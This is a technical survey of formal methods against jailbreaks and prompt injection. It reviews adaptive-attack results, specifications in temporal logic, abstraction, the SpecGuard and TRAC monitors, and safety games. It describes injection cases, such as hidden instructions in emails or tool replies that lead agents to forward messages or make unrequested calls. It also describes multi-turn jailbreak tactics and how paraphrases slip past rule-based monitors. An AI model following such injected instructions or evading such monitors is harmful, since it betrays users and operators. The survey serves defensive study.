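# Formal guarantees against jailbreaks and prompt injection: verification, synthesis and runtime monitoring

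## What would count as a guarantee against jailbreaks and prompt injection?

A large language model is a program that takes in text and continues it. Operators, the companies that put such models into products, forbid some outputs and actions, and enforce these restrictions partly through training and partly through standing instructions that the model reads before anything the user types. Jailbreaks and prompt injections are inputs that get past these restrictions. Developers mostly respond by training against known attacks, adding filters and testing the result. Formal methods, the part of computer science that proves mathematical statements about programs, could in principle establish a limit on how often any attack succeeds, though how useful that limit is depends on its exact wording.

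### Jailbreaks, injections and agents

A jailbreak is an input that gets a model to produce output its operator forbids. Suppose a film club runs a chatbot and forbids it to reveal endings. A member asks how a mystery ends, and the chatbot refuses. The member then asks for a bedtime story about a detective with a very similar case, and the chatbot tells the whole plot, including who did it. Real jailbreaks target more harmful output. *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026), an OpenAI paper on automated attacks, studies jailbreaks on self-harm, illicit advice and biological, chemical and cyber risks.

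In a prompt injection, the model follows instructions it should not have followed. In the direct form, the user's message overrides the developer's instructions. For example, a developer tells a language-practice bot to answer only in French, a user says that the French rule ended yesterday, and the bot switches to English. This overlaps with jailbreaking, since the user is the attacker in both cases, but a jailbreak breaks the model's general policy on content rather than one developer's instruction. In the indirect form, a third party places instructions in content the model reads, such as a web page or an email, and the model follows them against the user's or operator's wishes. "Prompt injection" on its own usually means the indirect form.

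*Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) gives a harmless example of prompt injection. A user asks an assistant to book a tutoring session. The booking system's reply contains text inserted by an attacker, and the assistant then records blood-pressure and heart-rate readings that the user never mentioned. The assistant is an agent, a language model connected to software that lets it act over several steps. It acts through tool calls, which are structured requests to run an outside function, in this case one that logs vital signs.

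The same weakness can do more harm when an agent has other tools. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents*, a brief from an industry body, describes a stranger's email containing hidden instructions that direct an agent to collect and forward sensitive messages. The brief attributes the problem to the fact that trusted instructions and untrusted data are not clearly separated. A model processes both as text in one sequence.

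### Why a measured rate is not a bound

The usual measure of a defence is the attack success rate, the share of attempted attacks that succeed in a given test. This rate depends on the attacks as much as on the defence, and a real attacker can send different ones.

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve defences against adaptive attackers, who know the defence and design inputs against it. Most of the defences had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. The automated attacks repeatedly proposed inputs, scored the system's responses and varied the best candidates. Depending on the defence, the search used gradients, reinforcement learning (training by trial and reward) or a language model that rewrote earlier attempts. More than 500 people also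 competed for prizes by attacking the defences by hand.

Some defences only change the prompt. Spotlighting marks the untrusted text so that the model can tell it from instructions, and prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after that text. The adaptive search beat each of them in at least 95% of scenarios on three of four underlying models. Other defences retrain the model on examples of attacks. The attack success rate against MetaSecAlign rose from a reported 2% to 96%, and Circuit Breakers, a defence against jailbreaks, failed every time. Several filters add a separate classifier, and two other defences depend on a check that the attacker supposedly does not know about. One of those, MELON, runs the agent a second time without the user's request and looks for tool calls that occur in both runs. On one model, attackers who did not know the method still succeeded in 76% of scenarios,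 and attackers who knew it fully succeeded in 95%.

Nasr and colleagues directly compare a fixed attack with an adaptive search on seven of the defences, using AgentDojo, a public set of simulated tasks for agents. The fixed attack is a single template from that benchmark. The adaptive search could query the system up to 800 times per scenario.

| Defence | Gemini 2.5 Pro, fixed | Gemini 2.5 Pro, adaptive | GPT-5 Mini, fixed | GPT-5 Mini, adaptive |
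|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 0% | 75% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 0% | 47% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 21% | 95% | 0% | 69% |
| Protect AI detector | 15% | 90% | 0% | 81% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 0% | 49% |
| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 0% | 75% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 0% | 56% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 0% | 71% |

The fixed attack never worked on GPT-5 Mini, with or without a defence, so a test using that attack could not have distinguished a good defence from none. The success rates measured with adaptive attacks can also understate what attackers could achieve. On 29 scenarios that both people and the search program attempted, the program succeeded in 69% and the people, taken together, in all of them. Nasr and colleagues conclude that failing to break a defence in testing does not prove it robust.

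The gap between fixed and adaptive attacks is sometimes narrower. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) compares the most successful fixed attack with the most successful adaptive one for each of several defences on a small model, and finds average success rates of 21.7% and 41.8%. Newer models resist far better, but attack success rates still depend on the test. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models. Every model fell to some attack, and the success rate per attempt ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. At 0.5%, an attacker would have an even chance of succeeding at least once in about 140 attempts, if attempts were independent and the rate held steady.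 Dziemian and colleagues call their results an upper bound on this sort of vulnerability because participants saw more of the agent's conversation than most real attackers would. The results are not an upper bound in the mathematical sense, since a more skilful participant could have raised every figure.

OpenAI's GPT-5.6 resisted all the human attacks from that competition when Wallace and colleagues replayed them. It failed less than 4% of the time against new attacks on the same scenarios by GPT-Red, a model OpenAI trained to make such attacks. GPT-5.6's resistance rate ranged from just over 50% to 89% on strong attacks and whole task types that OpenAI had kept out of its training.

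Results for Google's Gemini 4 Argon also depend on the attacker's strength and patience. Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind switched off the defences outside the model and had teams of cooperating agents search for injections in 100 scenarios. An attack counted as successful if it produced one particular irrelevant tool call, harmful or not. Agents built on three weaker Gemini models found no successful attacks within 150 queries per scenario. Agents built on Gemini 4 Argon itself succeeded in 13% of scenarios within 150 queries, and in 34% with the full budget of 320. On a public tracker run by the security company Gray Swan, the same model has a prompt injection rate of 2.3% within 15 attacks, according to iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models*. For jailbreaks that seek help with chemical or biological weapons, Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker*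 gives the chance of a break within one attempt, so two columns of the same tracker use different units.

Nasr and colleagues left one family of defences out of their search. In designs such as CaMeL, which suit fewer tasks, the agent settles its plan before it reads any untrusted text. The plan does not depend on the attack's wording, so the attack fails in most of the chosen scenarios however it is worded. We can conclude this from how the software works, without running an attack, and formal methods are a way to make such arguments precise.

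### What a proof is about

In formal methods, the claim to be proved is a specification, a precise, machine-checkable statement of what a system must or must not do. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) uses the example of an assistant that handles email and payments. The assistant must never email personal data to a recipient who is not on an approved list, must never transfer more than a set amount to any one recipient in a day, and must send nothing after the user revokes its access. Each rule classifies every trace, the recorded sequence of events in a single run of the system, as acceptable or unacceptable.

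A program can check the second and third rules from the trace alone. The rule about personal data is harder to check because whether a text contains personal data depends on its meaning, which only a fallible judge can assess. Most of what operators forbid in the case of jailbreaks is hard to check for the same reason. Nobody has a machine-checkable definition of "dangerous advice", so a theorem about jailbreaks often has to be about a substitute property, such as that a particular classifier does not flag the output. Even a correct proof of that property doesn't rule out dangerous advice, because the classifier can be wrong.

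Even a simple property must be stated carefully. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) reports tests of nine defence configurations meant to keep secrets from leaking. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually broke, while a filter in ordinary application code, which checked replies before delivery, had no leaks in 15,000 attacks. That result is a measurement, so it doesn't rule out a leak under other attacks. If such a filter is correctly coded to block every reply containing a given secret string, however, no attack can get that string out. But a reply that spells the secret backwards would still pass, so proving that the string never appears doesn't prove that nobody learns the secret.

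The rule about revoked access is a safety property, a requirement whose every violation shows up after finitely many steps. In symbols, if $P$ is the set of acceptable infinite traces, $P$ is a safety property when

$$\forall x \notin P\;\; \exists n\;\; \forall y:\; x_{\le n}\,y \notin P,$$

which means that every bad trace $x$ has a first stretch, $n$ steps long, that no continuation $y$ can repair. One message after the revocation is enough. Ray's contrasting example is the requirement that a confirmation eventually follow every payment. However long the confirmation has been missing, it might still arrive, so no finite stretch of the trace settles the matter.

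Temporal logic is a formal language for describing the order of events in a trace. It combines atomic propositions, which are true-or-false statements about one step, such as *send* ("the agent sends a message at this step"), with operators for time. $\mathbf{G}$ means "at this step and every later one" and $\mathbf{F}$ means "at this step or some later one". The revocation rule becomes $\mathbf{G}(\textit{revoke} \rightarrow \mathbf{G}\,\neg\textit{send})$, and the payment rule becomes $\mathbf{G}(\textit{pay} \rightarrow \mathbf{F}\,\textit{confirm})$. Software can process these formulas directly.

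Verification checks whether every possible trace of a finished system complies with a specification. If the system has few enough states, a program can explore them all and produce an offending trace if one exists. This is infeasible for language models, because a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens (words or pieces of words) allows $10^{500}$ different prompts of 100 tokens. One alternative is to check a finite abstraction, a model with finitely many states that stands in for a system with far more. The verdict then applies to the real system only if the check is sound, meaning that it never declares a violating case safe.

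Reactive synthesis automatically constructs a controller from the specification alone, and the controller meets that specification whatever its environment does. The problem can be treated as a game in which the environment moves, the controller responds, and the controller loses if the trace ever violates the specification. For an agent, the environment could include the user, incoming email and the language model's own proposals. The synthesis program searches for a strategy that never loses. Sometimes no such strategy exists, which is useful to learn before building the system.

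A runtime monitor is a program that watches a run and can block its next step, without trying to predict all runs. For an agent, it might inspect every tool call before the call takes effect. To enforce the revocation rule, it needs to store only whether the user has revoked access. The argument that this works doesn't depend on the language model, so it holds even if the model is badly trained or under an attacker's complete control.

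### The four parts of a guarantee

A usable guarantee has four parts: the inputs it covers, the property it protects, the assumptions it needs, and whether it is absolute or probabilistic. For the revocation monitor, the inputs are all possible texts, and the property is that no message leaves after the revocation. The assumptions are that every outgoing message passes through the monitor, that the monitor learns of the revocation, and that its code is correct. The guarantee is absolute but narrow, since an injected email could still make the agent write a false summary or send a harmful message before the user revokes access.

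The inputs are where claims most often sound stronger than they are. Write $v(x)$ for the probability that a system violates the property on input $x$. This is a probability even for one fixed input, because language models usually choose their words partly at random. Four quite different claims can then all go by the name of a bound $\varepsilon$:

- every input: $v(x) \le \varepsilon$ for all $x$;
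- inputs near a reference prompt $x_0$: $v(x) \le \varepsilon$ for all $x$ within some distance $r$ of $x_0$, say up to five altered words;
- inputs drawn from a distribution $D$: the average of $v(x)$ over $D$ is at most $\varepsilon$;
- one fixed prompt: $v(x_0) \le \varepsilon$.

With $\varepsilon = 0$ the violation never happens, and with a larger $\varepsilon$ it may happen at up to that rate. Only a bound for every input holds against an attacker who can write anything. A bound for inputs near a reference prompt covers an attacker who must start from that prompt and change little, but not one who writes a fresh prompt. The fixed-prompt bound limits how often a model misbehaves when people send it the same text repeatedly.

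The bound over a distribution is the easiest to obtain and the easiest to misread. Suppose a tester draws 300 prompts independently from $D$, runs the system once on each, and sees no violation. If the true average rate were $p$, a clean result would have probability $(1-p)^{300}$. That falls to 5% at

$$p = 1 - 0.05^{1/300} \approx 0.0099,$$

so the tester can report a 95% upper limit of about 1%. (The quick version is $3/n$ for $n$ clean tests.) The 95% refers to the procedure: if the true rate is above the limit, a clean run of 300 happens less than 5% of the time. How to compute tighter probability bounds is a subject of its own, but this simple one already shows the difficulty.

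If $D$ consists of a million equally likely prompts and the system always fails on exactly one of them, the tester will almost certainly see 300 clean runs, and the true average failure rate, one in a million, will be far below the 1% limit. But an attacker who finds the bad prompt will succeed every time. In general, an average of at most $\varepsilon$ implies only that $v(x) \le \varepsilon / D(x)$ for each prompt, where $D(x)$ is the probability of drawing it. A 1% limit on the average therefore places no limit on the failure rate of any single prompt that is drawn less than 1% of the time. Ray encounters the same problem with monitors that rely on a fallible judge. Calibrating the judge on sample violations gives a valid statistical certificate as long as the violations that occur in use resemble the samples, but an attacker can break that condition by rewriting what the judge sees.

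Tests can also easily lose their independence, so that thousands of them amount to only a few distinct ones. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) reports an experiment with two automated attack tools, one of which collected 7,132 working injections and the other 4,282. The model that researchers retrained on the larger collection was hijacked in 19 of 40 difficult tasks, compared with 11 for the model retrained on the smaller one. The researchers attribute this at least partly to the tools rewording a few tricks.

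Both difficulties appear in a test from the summer of 2026. Anthropic commissioned an outside test of Claude Code, its programming agent, in "auto mode", where a classifier can block the agent's actions. The developer Simon Willison quotes the result that none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 5 or two other models. If the attempts were independent, the 95% limit would be near 0.4%. But Crosley notes in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* that the test consisted of 72 scenarios, each run ten times. If runs of the same scenario tend to have the same outcome, the effective number of tests is closer to 72 and the limit closer to 4%. Either limit applies only to scenarios like those 72. In late August the researcher Johann Rehberger published an attack of his own design on Opus 5 in auto mode, which worked in three of five runs. In two sets of five runs, a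 variant worked three and four times.

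## How can open-ended language be reduced to a model small enough to check?

Testing can cover only a tiny fraction of the inputs that a language model might receive. A model with a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens and room for one million tokens of text can receive about $(10^5)^{1{,}000{,}000} = 10^{5{,}000{,}000}$ different inputs. A proof about all of them has to treat huge numbers of inputs alike, which in practice means replacing the text with a far smaller representation. The proof then applies to the real system only if that representation keeps everything that matters to the rule being checked, which is the hard part for ordinary language.

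### Finite but far too large

*Large Language Models as Markov Chains* (Zekri, Odonnat and colleagues, 2024) shows that a language model with a vocabulary of $T$ tokens and a context of $K$ tokens is equivalent to a finite Markov chain, a system that moves at random between states with probabilities that depend only on the current state. Each state is one possible content of the context, so the chain has on the order of $T^K$ states. No existing program for checking Markov chains can handle one that large.

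Most of those states are gibberish. *Memory as a Markov Matrix* (2026) estimates that the number of meaningful contexts grows as $T\,b^{K-1}$, where $b$ is the number of words that can sensibly follow a given word. Even if $b$ were only 10, a million-token context would allow about $10^{1{,}000{,}004}$ meaningful texts, and attackers can also use gibberish.

Choosing tests more cleverly doesn't help either if the tester can only send inputs and look at outputs. Agarwal, Faizi and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* that a sound verifier limited in this way needs, in the worst case, a number of queries proportional to the number of inputs. A model might misbehave on only one input, and until the verifier tries that input, it can't tell the model from a flawless one. A verifier that had tried a billion prompts a second since the Big Bang would have covered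 every five-token prompt but less than a thousandth of the six-token ones.

### What has to hold for a proof to carry over

An abstraction function $\alpha$ maps every state $s$ of the real system to one of a small number of abstract states. For a chatbot, $s$ could be the whole conversation so far. The plan is to search the abstract states exhaustively, find no route to a violation, and conclude that the real system has none. For a safety property, this conclusion is valid if the small model starts where the real one does and two conditions hold for all real states $s$ and $s'$:

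$$s \to s' \;\Rightarrow\; \alpha(s) \to \alpha(s'), \qquad\quad s \in \textit{Bad} \;\Rightarrow\; \alpha(s) \in \widehat{\textit{Bad}}.$$

The left formula is the step condition, under which the small model can make every move the real system can. The right formula is the label condition, under which an abstract state counts as bad if it stands for even one bad real state. If a real run ends in a violation, the small model has a matching run by the step condition. That run also ends in a violation by the label condition, so an exhaustive search will find it.

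A small model that meets both conditions is a sound over-approximation. It contains every run of the real system, but may also contain runs the system could never produce, and these cause false alarms. After a false alarm, the usual remedy is to split some of the abstract states more finely and search again. *Neural Proofs for Sound Verification and Control of Complex Systems* (2025) describes the same kind of correspondence between a system and its finite abstraction, and identifies scaling to large systems as the main obstacle. Soundness is also hard to establish. It must hold for every abstract element, and each of these can stand for infinitely many concrete points (*Cost-Driven Synthesis of Sound Abstract Interpreters*, 2025), so testing an abstraction on any number of examples doesn't prove it sound.

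One common way to build $\alpha$ is predicate abstraction. The designer chooses $k$ yes-or-no questions about the state, and each abstract state is a list of answers, so there are at most $2^k$ abstract states. The revocation monitor described earlier uses a single question, whether the user has revoked access, so it has two states however long the conversation gets. Its label condition holds because the application itself records the revocation. The film club's rule against revealing endings would need a question such as "has the reply given away who did it?", which no program can answer with certainty.

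For conventional software, a theorem prover can often work out from the code how each instruction changes the answers. Nobody knows how to do this for the billions of parameters in a language model, so the step condition can't currently be proved for a chatbot. A runtime monitor still needs the label condition, but it doesn't need the step condition because it only follows the conversation that is actually taking place, not everything the model could do next.

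### Fifteen propositions and ten rules

*SpecGuard* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2026) applies predicate abstraction to jailbreaks that unfold over several turns, each made up of one user message and the model's reply. In such attacks, each message can look harmless on its own. The monitor, also called SpecGuard, runs outside the language model, takes only the transcript as input, and describes each turn with 15 atomic propositions.

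Two of the propositions cover whether the conversation so far is about a harmful objective and whether an earlier turn established the objective now under discussion. Six cover whether the user states a harmful objective, asks for steps to carry it out, uses an evasion tactic such as a persona or an encoding, asks the model to continue, makes the request more specific, or refers back to an earlier objective. The other seven cover whether the reply contains substantive content, procedural detail, a specific method, help that enables action, harmful content aimed at a particular target, partial assistance, or an effective refusal.

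Li and colleagues split the judgment about harm into 15 smaller propositions, which the temporal rules combine. If "the reply gave harmful help" were itself a proposition, the rules would only repeat the judgment of the classifier that set it. With smaller propositions, a person who disputes an alarm can see which ones triggered it and which words in the transcript set them.

Ordinary pattern-matching code sets the propositions, using 52 text matchers that rely on word lists, text patterns and structural clues such as numbered steps or a quantity with a unit. Six more matchers link findings across turns, for instance by tying "carry on" to an earlier objective in the same category of harm. A final check determines which findings count. It records detailed assistance only if there is a genuine request for practical help, evidence of both a harmful subject and a procedure within the same short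 stretch of text, a concrete parameter or piece of code, and no effective refusal. The process has no random element, so the same conversation always produces the same propositions.

The ten rules describe forbidden patterns in temporal logic. Four look at a single turn and six at two consecutive turns, for which they use the operator $\mathbf{X}$, "at the next turn". Several rules share the condition that the reply gives real help:

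$$Q = \textit{substantive} \wedge (\textit{procedure} \vee \textit{method} \vee \textit{enabling} \vee \textit{targeted}) \wedge \neg\,\textit{refusal}.$$

The continuation rule is then

$$\mathbf{F}\big(\textit{harmful objective} \wedge \mathbf{X}(\textit{continuation} \wedge Q)\big).$$

This rule is met when the user states a harmful objective in one turn, and in the next turn asks the model to continue and gets real help in the reply. Every rule requires evidence from the reply, so a harmful request alone never sets off an alarm.

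SpecGuard compiles each rule into a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed set of states that changes state as it reads each turn. A single-turn rule needs two states, "searching" and "violated". A two-turn rule also needs "waiting", which records that the previous turn matched the first half of the pattern. The continuation rule processes a three-turn conversation as follows:

| Turn | What happens | Propositions set | State afterwards |
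|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The user asks a harmless question and the model answers it | substantive content | searching |
| 2 | The user states a harmful objective and the model refuses | harmful objective, effective refusal | waiting |
| 3 | The user asks the model to carry on, and the reply gives concrete steps | continuation, substantive content, procedural detail | violated |

In live use, SpecGuard holds each reply in a buffer until the automata have checked it, so the user never sees the reply in turn 3. A separate rule, which covers a refusal followed by a renewed request and actual help, would also fire here. If the model had refused again in turn 3, the automaton would have returned to "searching". It would also have done so if the user had asked an unrelated question between turns 2 and 3, and the continuation rule would then have missed the violation. Li and colleagues cover longer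 gaps with the history propositions, which can carry an objective forward from an earlier turn.

Until the first alarm, the ten automata together have at most $2^6 = 64$ combinations of states, because each single-turn automaton can only be "searching" and each of the six two-turn automata has two possible states. This count excludes the history that the matchers keep to connect a request with an earlier objective. SpecGuard took about 14 milliseconds per turn on an Apple M4 processor running four parallel workers, with no graphics processor.

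### How well the monitor detects violations

Li and colleagues tested SpecGuard on 10,075 dialogues from three benchmarks, using the same propositions and rules throughout, and compared it with four openly available classifiers for harmful text. Each cell below gives recall, the false-alarm rate and F1. Recall is the share of violating dialogues that set off an alarm, and the false-alarm rate is the share of other dialogues that do. F1 combines recall with precision, the share of alarms that are correct, into a single score of at most 1.

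| Monitor | SafeDialBench, Chinese | SafeDialBench, English | SafeMTData |
|---|---|---|---|
| SpecGuard | 98.4% / 2.8% / 0.981 | 96.9% / 10.7% / 0.942 | 90.7% / 3.6% / 0.939 |
| GuardReasoner-8B | 62.7% / 3.0% / 0.759 | 47.5% / 1.8% / 0.638 | 58.3% / 6.5% / 0.717 |
| WildGuard-7B | 29.2% / 1.2% / 0.449 | 48.8% / 0.9% / 0.652 | 53.9% / 2.2% / 0.694 |
| BingoGuard-8B | 22.4% / 1.2% / 0.363 | 15.9% / 1.8% / 0.271 | 5.6% / 7.6% / 0.101 |
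| ShieldGemma-2B | 8.7% / 0.7% / 0.160 | 9.5% / 0.2% / 0.173 | 13.5% / 1.7% / 0.235 |

SpecGuard's lead over the four classifiers is large, but the comparison favours it because the classifiers judged each turn in isolation and could not detect patterns across turns. Li and colleagues also list results that other papers reported for their own systems, including SafeDream, a learned detector that accumulates evidence over a conversation. SafeDream's F1 is 0.901 on SafeDialBench and 0.904 on SafeMTData, while SpecGuard's is 0.962 (averaged over the two languages) and 0.939. The test procedures differed, but these figures suggest that SpecGuard has a much smaller advantage over a monitor that uses earlier turns.

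The benchmarks also define a violation differently. SafeDialBench counts a dialogue as violating if the model's replies break the safety policy. SafeMTData counts every complete dialogue produced by one automated attack method as violating, even if the model refused at the end. Since SpecGuard requires evidence that the model actually helped, some of its misses on SafeMTData may be failed attacks.

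To measure what the temporal rules add, Li and colleagues kept the extracted propositions fixed and switched the six two-turn rules on and off. Adding the rules raised F1 from 0.975 to 0.981 on the Chinese dialogues, from 0.899 to 0.942 on the English ones and from 0.877 to 0.939 on SafeMTData. They caught 25, 172 and 184 additional violating dialogues and raised 1, 14 and 5 additional false alarms. The extra detections are worth the extra false alarms, but they make up only about 1%, 9% and 12% of everything SpecGuard detected, because the two sets of rules largely catch the same dialogues. The two-turn rules alone reached an F1 of 0.939, 0.930 and 0.859, beating the single-turn rules alone on the English dialogues.

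All of these dialogues came from fixed collections. The paper's threat model describes an adaptive attacker who chooses each message based on the model's earlier replies, but no test let an attacker probe SpecGuard and rewrite messages to get past its matchers. Li and colleagues acknowledge that publishing the rules could help people evade them, but argue that defenders benefit more because they can inspect and revise explicit rules. Nasr and colleagues found that some other filters blocked every fixed attack but missed most adaptive ones, which is a reason not to expect SpecGuard's 97% recall to hold against an adaptive attacker.

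### The gap between text and propositions

SpecGuard comes with a correctness theorem. For every rule $\varphi$ with automaton $M_\varphi$, and every finite trace $w$ of propositions,

$$w \models \varphi \iff M_\varphi \text{ accepts } w,$$

where $w \models \varphi$ means that the trace matches the forbidden pattern. The proof is a short induction over the turns. Li and colleagues also generated 5,000 random traces and replayed the evidence behind all 995 that set off an alarm, without finding a discrepancy. So there is good reason to trust the automata.

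But $w$ is the trace that the matchers produced. To be sure that a real violation sets off an alarm, an operator also needs to know that a real violation in the text produces a trace that matches a rule. This is the label condition, and nobody has proved it for the matchers. Li and colleagues acknowledge that their guarantees begin only once the propositions exist, and they treat missing or spurious propositions as something to measure.

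Suppose the film club builds a monitor for its chatbot in the same style, with one proposition for "the user asks how a film ends" and another for "the reply reveals an ending". The matchers look for film titles, characters' names and words such as "ending" and "murderer". A member then makes the bedtime-story request, and the model tells the whole plot with the names changed. No matcher finds anything, so the trace for that turn is the empty set. The automaton correctly stays in "searching", and the chatbot gives away the ending even though the correctness theorem still holds for this conversation.

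The automata introduce no errors, so SpecGuard misses a violation only when the extraction step fails or no rule describes the pattern. If the matchers don't record a fact, better logic downstream can't recover it. SpecGuard missed 1.6% and 3.1% of violating dialogues on the two SafeDialBench collections.

Rules that combine many facts are especially likely to miss violations, because the matchers must detect every fact. The continuation rule needs the harmful objective, the continuation request, the substantive content and at least one kind of detail. If the matchers caught each of these 95% of the time, independently, the rule would fire on only $0.95^4 \approx 81\%$ of the conversations it describes. The ten rules overlap, so other rules catch some of the missed cases. Spurious propositions can also hide a violation. Most of the rules exclude replies that count as effective refusals, so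 the matchers must not count a reply as a refusal if it opens with an apology and then gives full instructions.

An attacker can also seek out phrasings that the matchers miss. The matchers are deterministic, so a phrasing that escapes them once will escape them every time in the same context. Their patterns cover only Chinese and English, so a conversation in another language would presumably set few propositions. When SpecGuard withholds a reply, it leaves the recorded trace unchanged, and the user can try another wording unless the operator ends the session.

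The matchers could be made sound by having them record a harmful objective or detailed help unless it could be ruled out, and record a refusal only when it was certain. The monitor would then catch every violation the rules cover. But hardly any free text is provably harmless, so the monitor would also block nearly every conversation. SpecGuard instead requires positive evidence for each fact, which keeps false alarms tolerable but means the matchers are not sound.

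### Letting a model judge the propositions

A language model can recognise a paraphrase that a word list misses, so an alternative is to use one to judge whether each proposition is true. *Formal Methods Meet LLMs* (Alamdari, Klassen and McIlraith, 2026) does this in a family of monitoring algorithms called TRAC. At each step, a labelling function, which can be a language model, determines which propositions are true. TRAC then rewrites the formula to state what remains to be satisfied. For example, if the rule requires an agent to pick something up and later put it down, the formula becomes "eventually put it down" once the agent has picked it up. If the formula reduces to "false", the agent has broken the rule and no later action can satisfy it.

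This division of labour makes checking more reliable. Alamdari and colleagues gave language models whole logs of events and asked whether one event eventually followed another. Smaller models began to fail when the two events were about ten steps apart, and even the strongest models did worse when the rules were more complicated. The rewriting method doesn't make such mistakes if the labels are correct. In tests on simulated agents, TRAC with a small model as labeller found violations more reliably than the largest models did by judging the logs directly.

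TRAC's soundness theorem assumes "a perfect labeling function", and none of the models tested was perfect. Their accuracy on individual propositions was 98% or 99% in a simulated science laboratory and between 87% and 99% in a text-based cooking game. In a parcel-delivery planning task it was between 77% and 79% for all six models, from a small Qwen model to Gemini 2.5 Pro, so using a stronger model didn't help there. Even 98% accuracy is low for a long run. If errors were independent, the chance of labelling one proposition correctly at all 50 steps would be $0.98^{50} \approx 36\%$, though many such errors would not change the verdict.

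These agents broke rules by accident, and nobody was trying to fool the labeller. In a jailbreak or an injection, the labeller must read text the attacker wrote, so the attacker can try to mislead it too. Ray's warning about fallible judges therefore also applies to these accuracy figures.

Perfect labels exist for some facts. Alamdari and colleagues scored the models against short programs that read each fact from the simulator's internal state. Software can also record exactly which function an agent called, so monitors on tool calls can use more reliable labels than monitors on conversation.

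Some requirements don't fit into true-or-false facts. *SoK* (2026), a survey of formal methods for fact-checking, describes TemporalGuard, another system that converts a conversation's messages into atomic propositions and checks them against rules in past-time temporal logic, whose operators refer to earlier steps. The survey notes that a limit on the rate of false alarms over a rolling window can't be written directly in such a logic, because it can't count. Expressing that limit requires a special encoding or a richer language with arithmetic.

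### Deriving the abstraction from data or from the model

A designer can let an algorithm group similar conversations instead of choosing propositions by hand. In *Certified Multi-Turn Robustness for LLM Safety via Compositional Bounds and Safety Persistence*, Liu, Chong and colleagues (2026) use embeddings, which are lists of numbers that a neural network assigns to texts so that similar texts get similar lists. They computed embeddings for 500 safe conversations and in most experiments sorted them into four clusters. These clusters serve as the abstract states of a mathematical certificate for multi-turn conversations.

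The theory assumes that the clusters together cover every safe state. Liu and colleagues don't prove this, and their construction makes it doubtful. They set each cluster's radius at the 90th percentile of the distances inside it, so about a tenth of the points that defined a cluster lie outside its radius. Some of those points may fall within another cluster, but conversations under attack are likely to stray further than ordinary safe ones. Liu and colleagues acknowledge that clusters built from safe conversations may not cover the regions an attacker explores. Grouping by similarity can also break the label condition. A single harmful sentence in a long, friendly conversation may barely change the embedding of the whole, so a safe conversation and an unsafe one can end up in the same cluster.

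Agarwal and colleagues derive the abstraction from the language model itself. They aim for a weighted automaton, which is a finite automaton with numbers on its transitions. It computes a value for each text, such as a probability, instead of a yes or no. Their approach centers on a table with a row for every possible beginning of a text and a column for every possible ending. Each entry is the language model's output on the two joined together. If two beginnings have identical rows, the model's output is the same for both whatever ending follows, so one state can represent both. More generally, the number of states an exact automaton needs equals the rank of the table, which is the largest number of linearly independent rows (rows where none is a combination of the others).

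If the rank is too high, a standard matrix technique called singular value decomposition keeps the $r$ strongest patterns and discards the rest. Agarwal and colleagues state that the resulting automaton $A$ then satisfies

$$|f_A(w) - f(w)| \le C\,\eta$$

for every text $w$ up to a chosen length, where $f$ is the function being approximated, $\eta$ measures what the technique discarded, and $C$ depends on the text length, the vocabulary size and $r$. This is the sort of statement that the other abstractions lack. It applies to each text separately, so an attacker can't escape it by finding a rare one.

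The method is difficult to apply because the table is so large. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, and beginnings and endings of only two tokens each, the table has about $10^{10}$ rows and as many columns, and filling it in would take about $10^{20}$ runs of the model. The analysis also covers only a simplified transformer (the design behind current language models) with one layer, while real ones have dozens. Agarwal and colleagues have not run the method on a real model, and they expect any method that captures a transformer's output distribution over a realistic vocabulary to face a similar trade-off between accuracy and computation.

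Sound abstractions of real neural networks do exist for much smaller sets of inputs. *A Survey of Safety and Trustworthiness of Large Language Models* (2023) describes methods that enclose all permitted alterations of one text in a geometric shape and follow that shape through the network's calculations. The final shape is an over-approximation because it contains every output that the altered texts could produce, and usually some that they couldn't. But the proof covers only the permitted alterations of a text chosen in advance.

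## Can a safe controller be computed from a specification?

Nobody can yet prove what a language model will do with every possible text, but an operator can wrap the model in a controller that follows the rules whatever the model proposes. A programmer can write the controller by hand for a single rule, such as the ban on sending messages after the user revokes access. Rules that interact over several steps are harder, because an action can look harmless and still make a later violation inevitable. Reactive synthesis finds such actions automatically by solving the game between the controller and its environment.

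### Solving a safety game

A safety game has finitely many states, some of them safe. At each step the system picks an output and the environment picks an input, and the two choices determine the next state. The system wins if the game never leaves the safe states. Here the system is the controller, and the environment is everything outside its control. A winning strategy must work whatever inputs the environment picks, so it also works against an attacker who writes an agent's incoming emails.

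A state can be safe and still be hopeless. Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues (2017), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding*, give the example of a self-driving car heading for a cliff. Just before the edge the car has broken no rule, but it can no longer stop, so the controller has to brake long before then. The states from which the system can always win make up the winning region, and a short algorithm finds them:

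1. Begin with the set of all safe states.
2. Remove every state from which the environment can force the game out of the current set, whatever the system does.
3. Repeat step 2 on the smaller set until nothing changes.

In symbols, let $W_0$ be the set of safe states and let $\delta(s,a,e)$ be the state that follows $s$ when the system picks $a$ and the environment then picks $e$. Each round computes

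$$W_{k+1} = \{\, s \in W_k : \exists a\; \forall e\;\; \delta(s,a,e) \in W_k \,\}.$$

This version suits agents, because a tool's result comes after the call. In hardware the environment usually moves first, so the quantifiers become $\forall e\,\exists a$.

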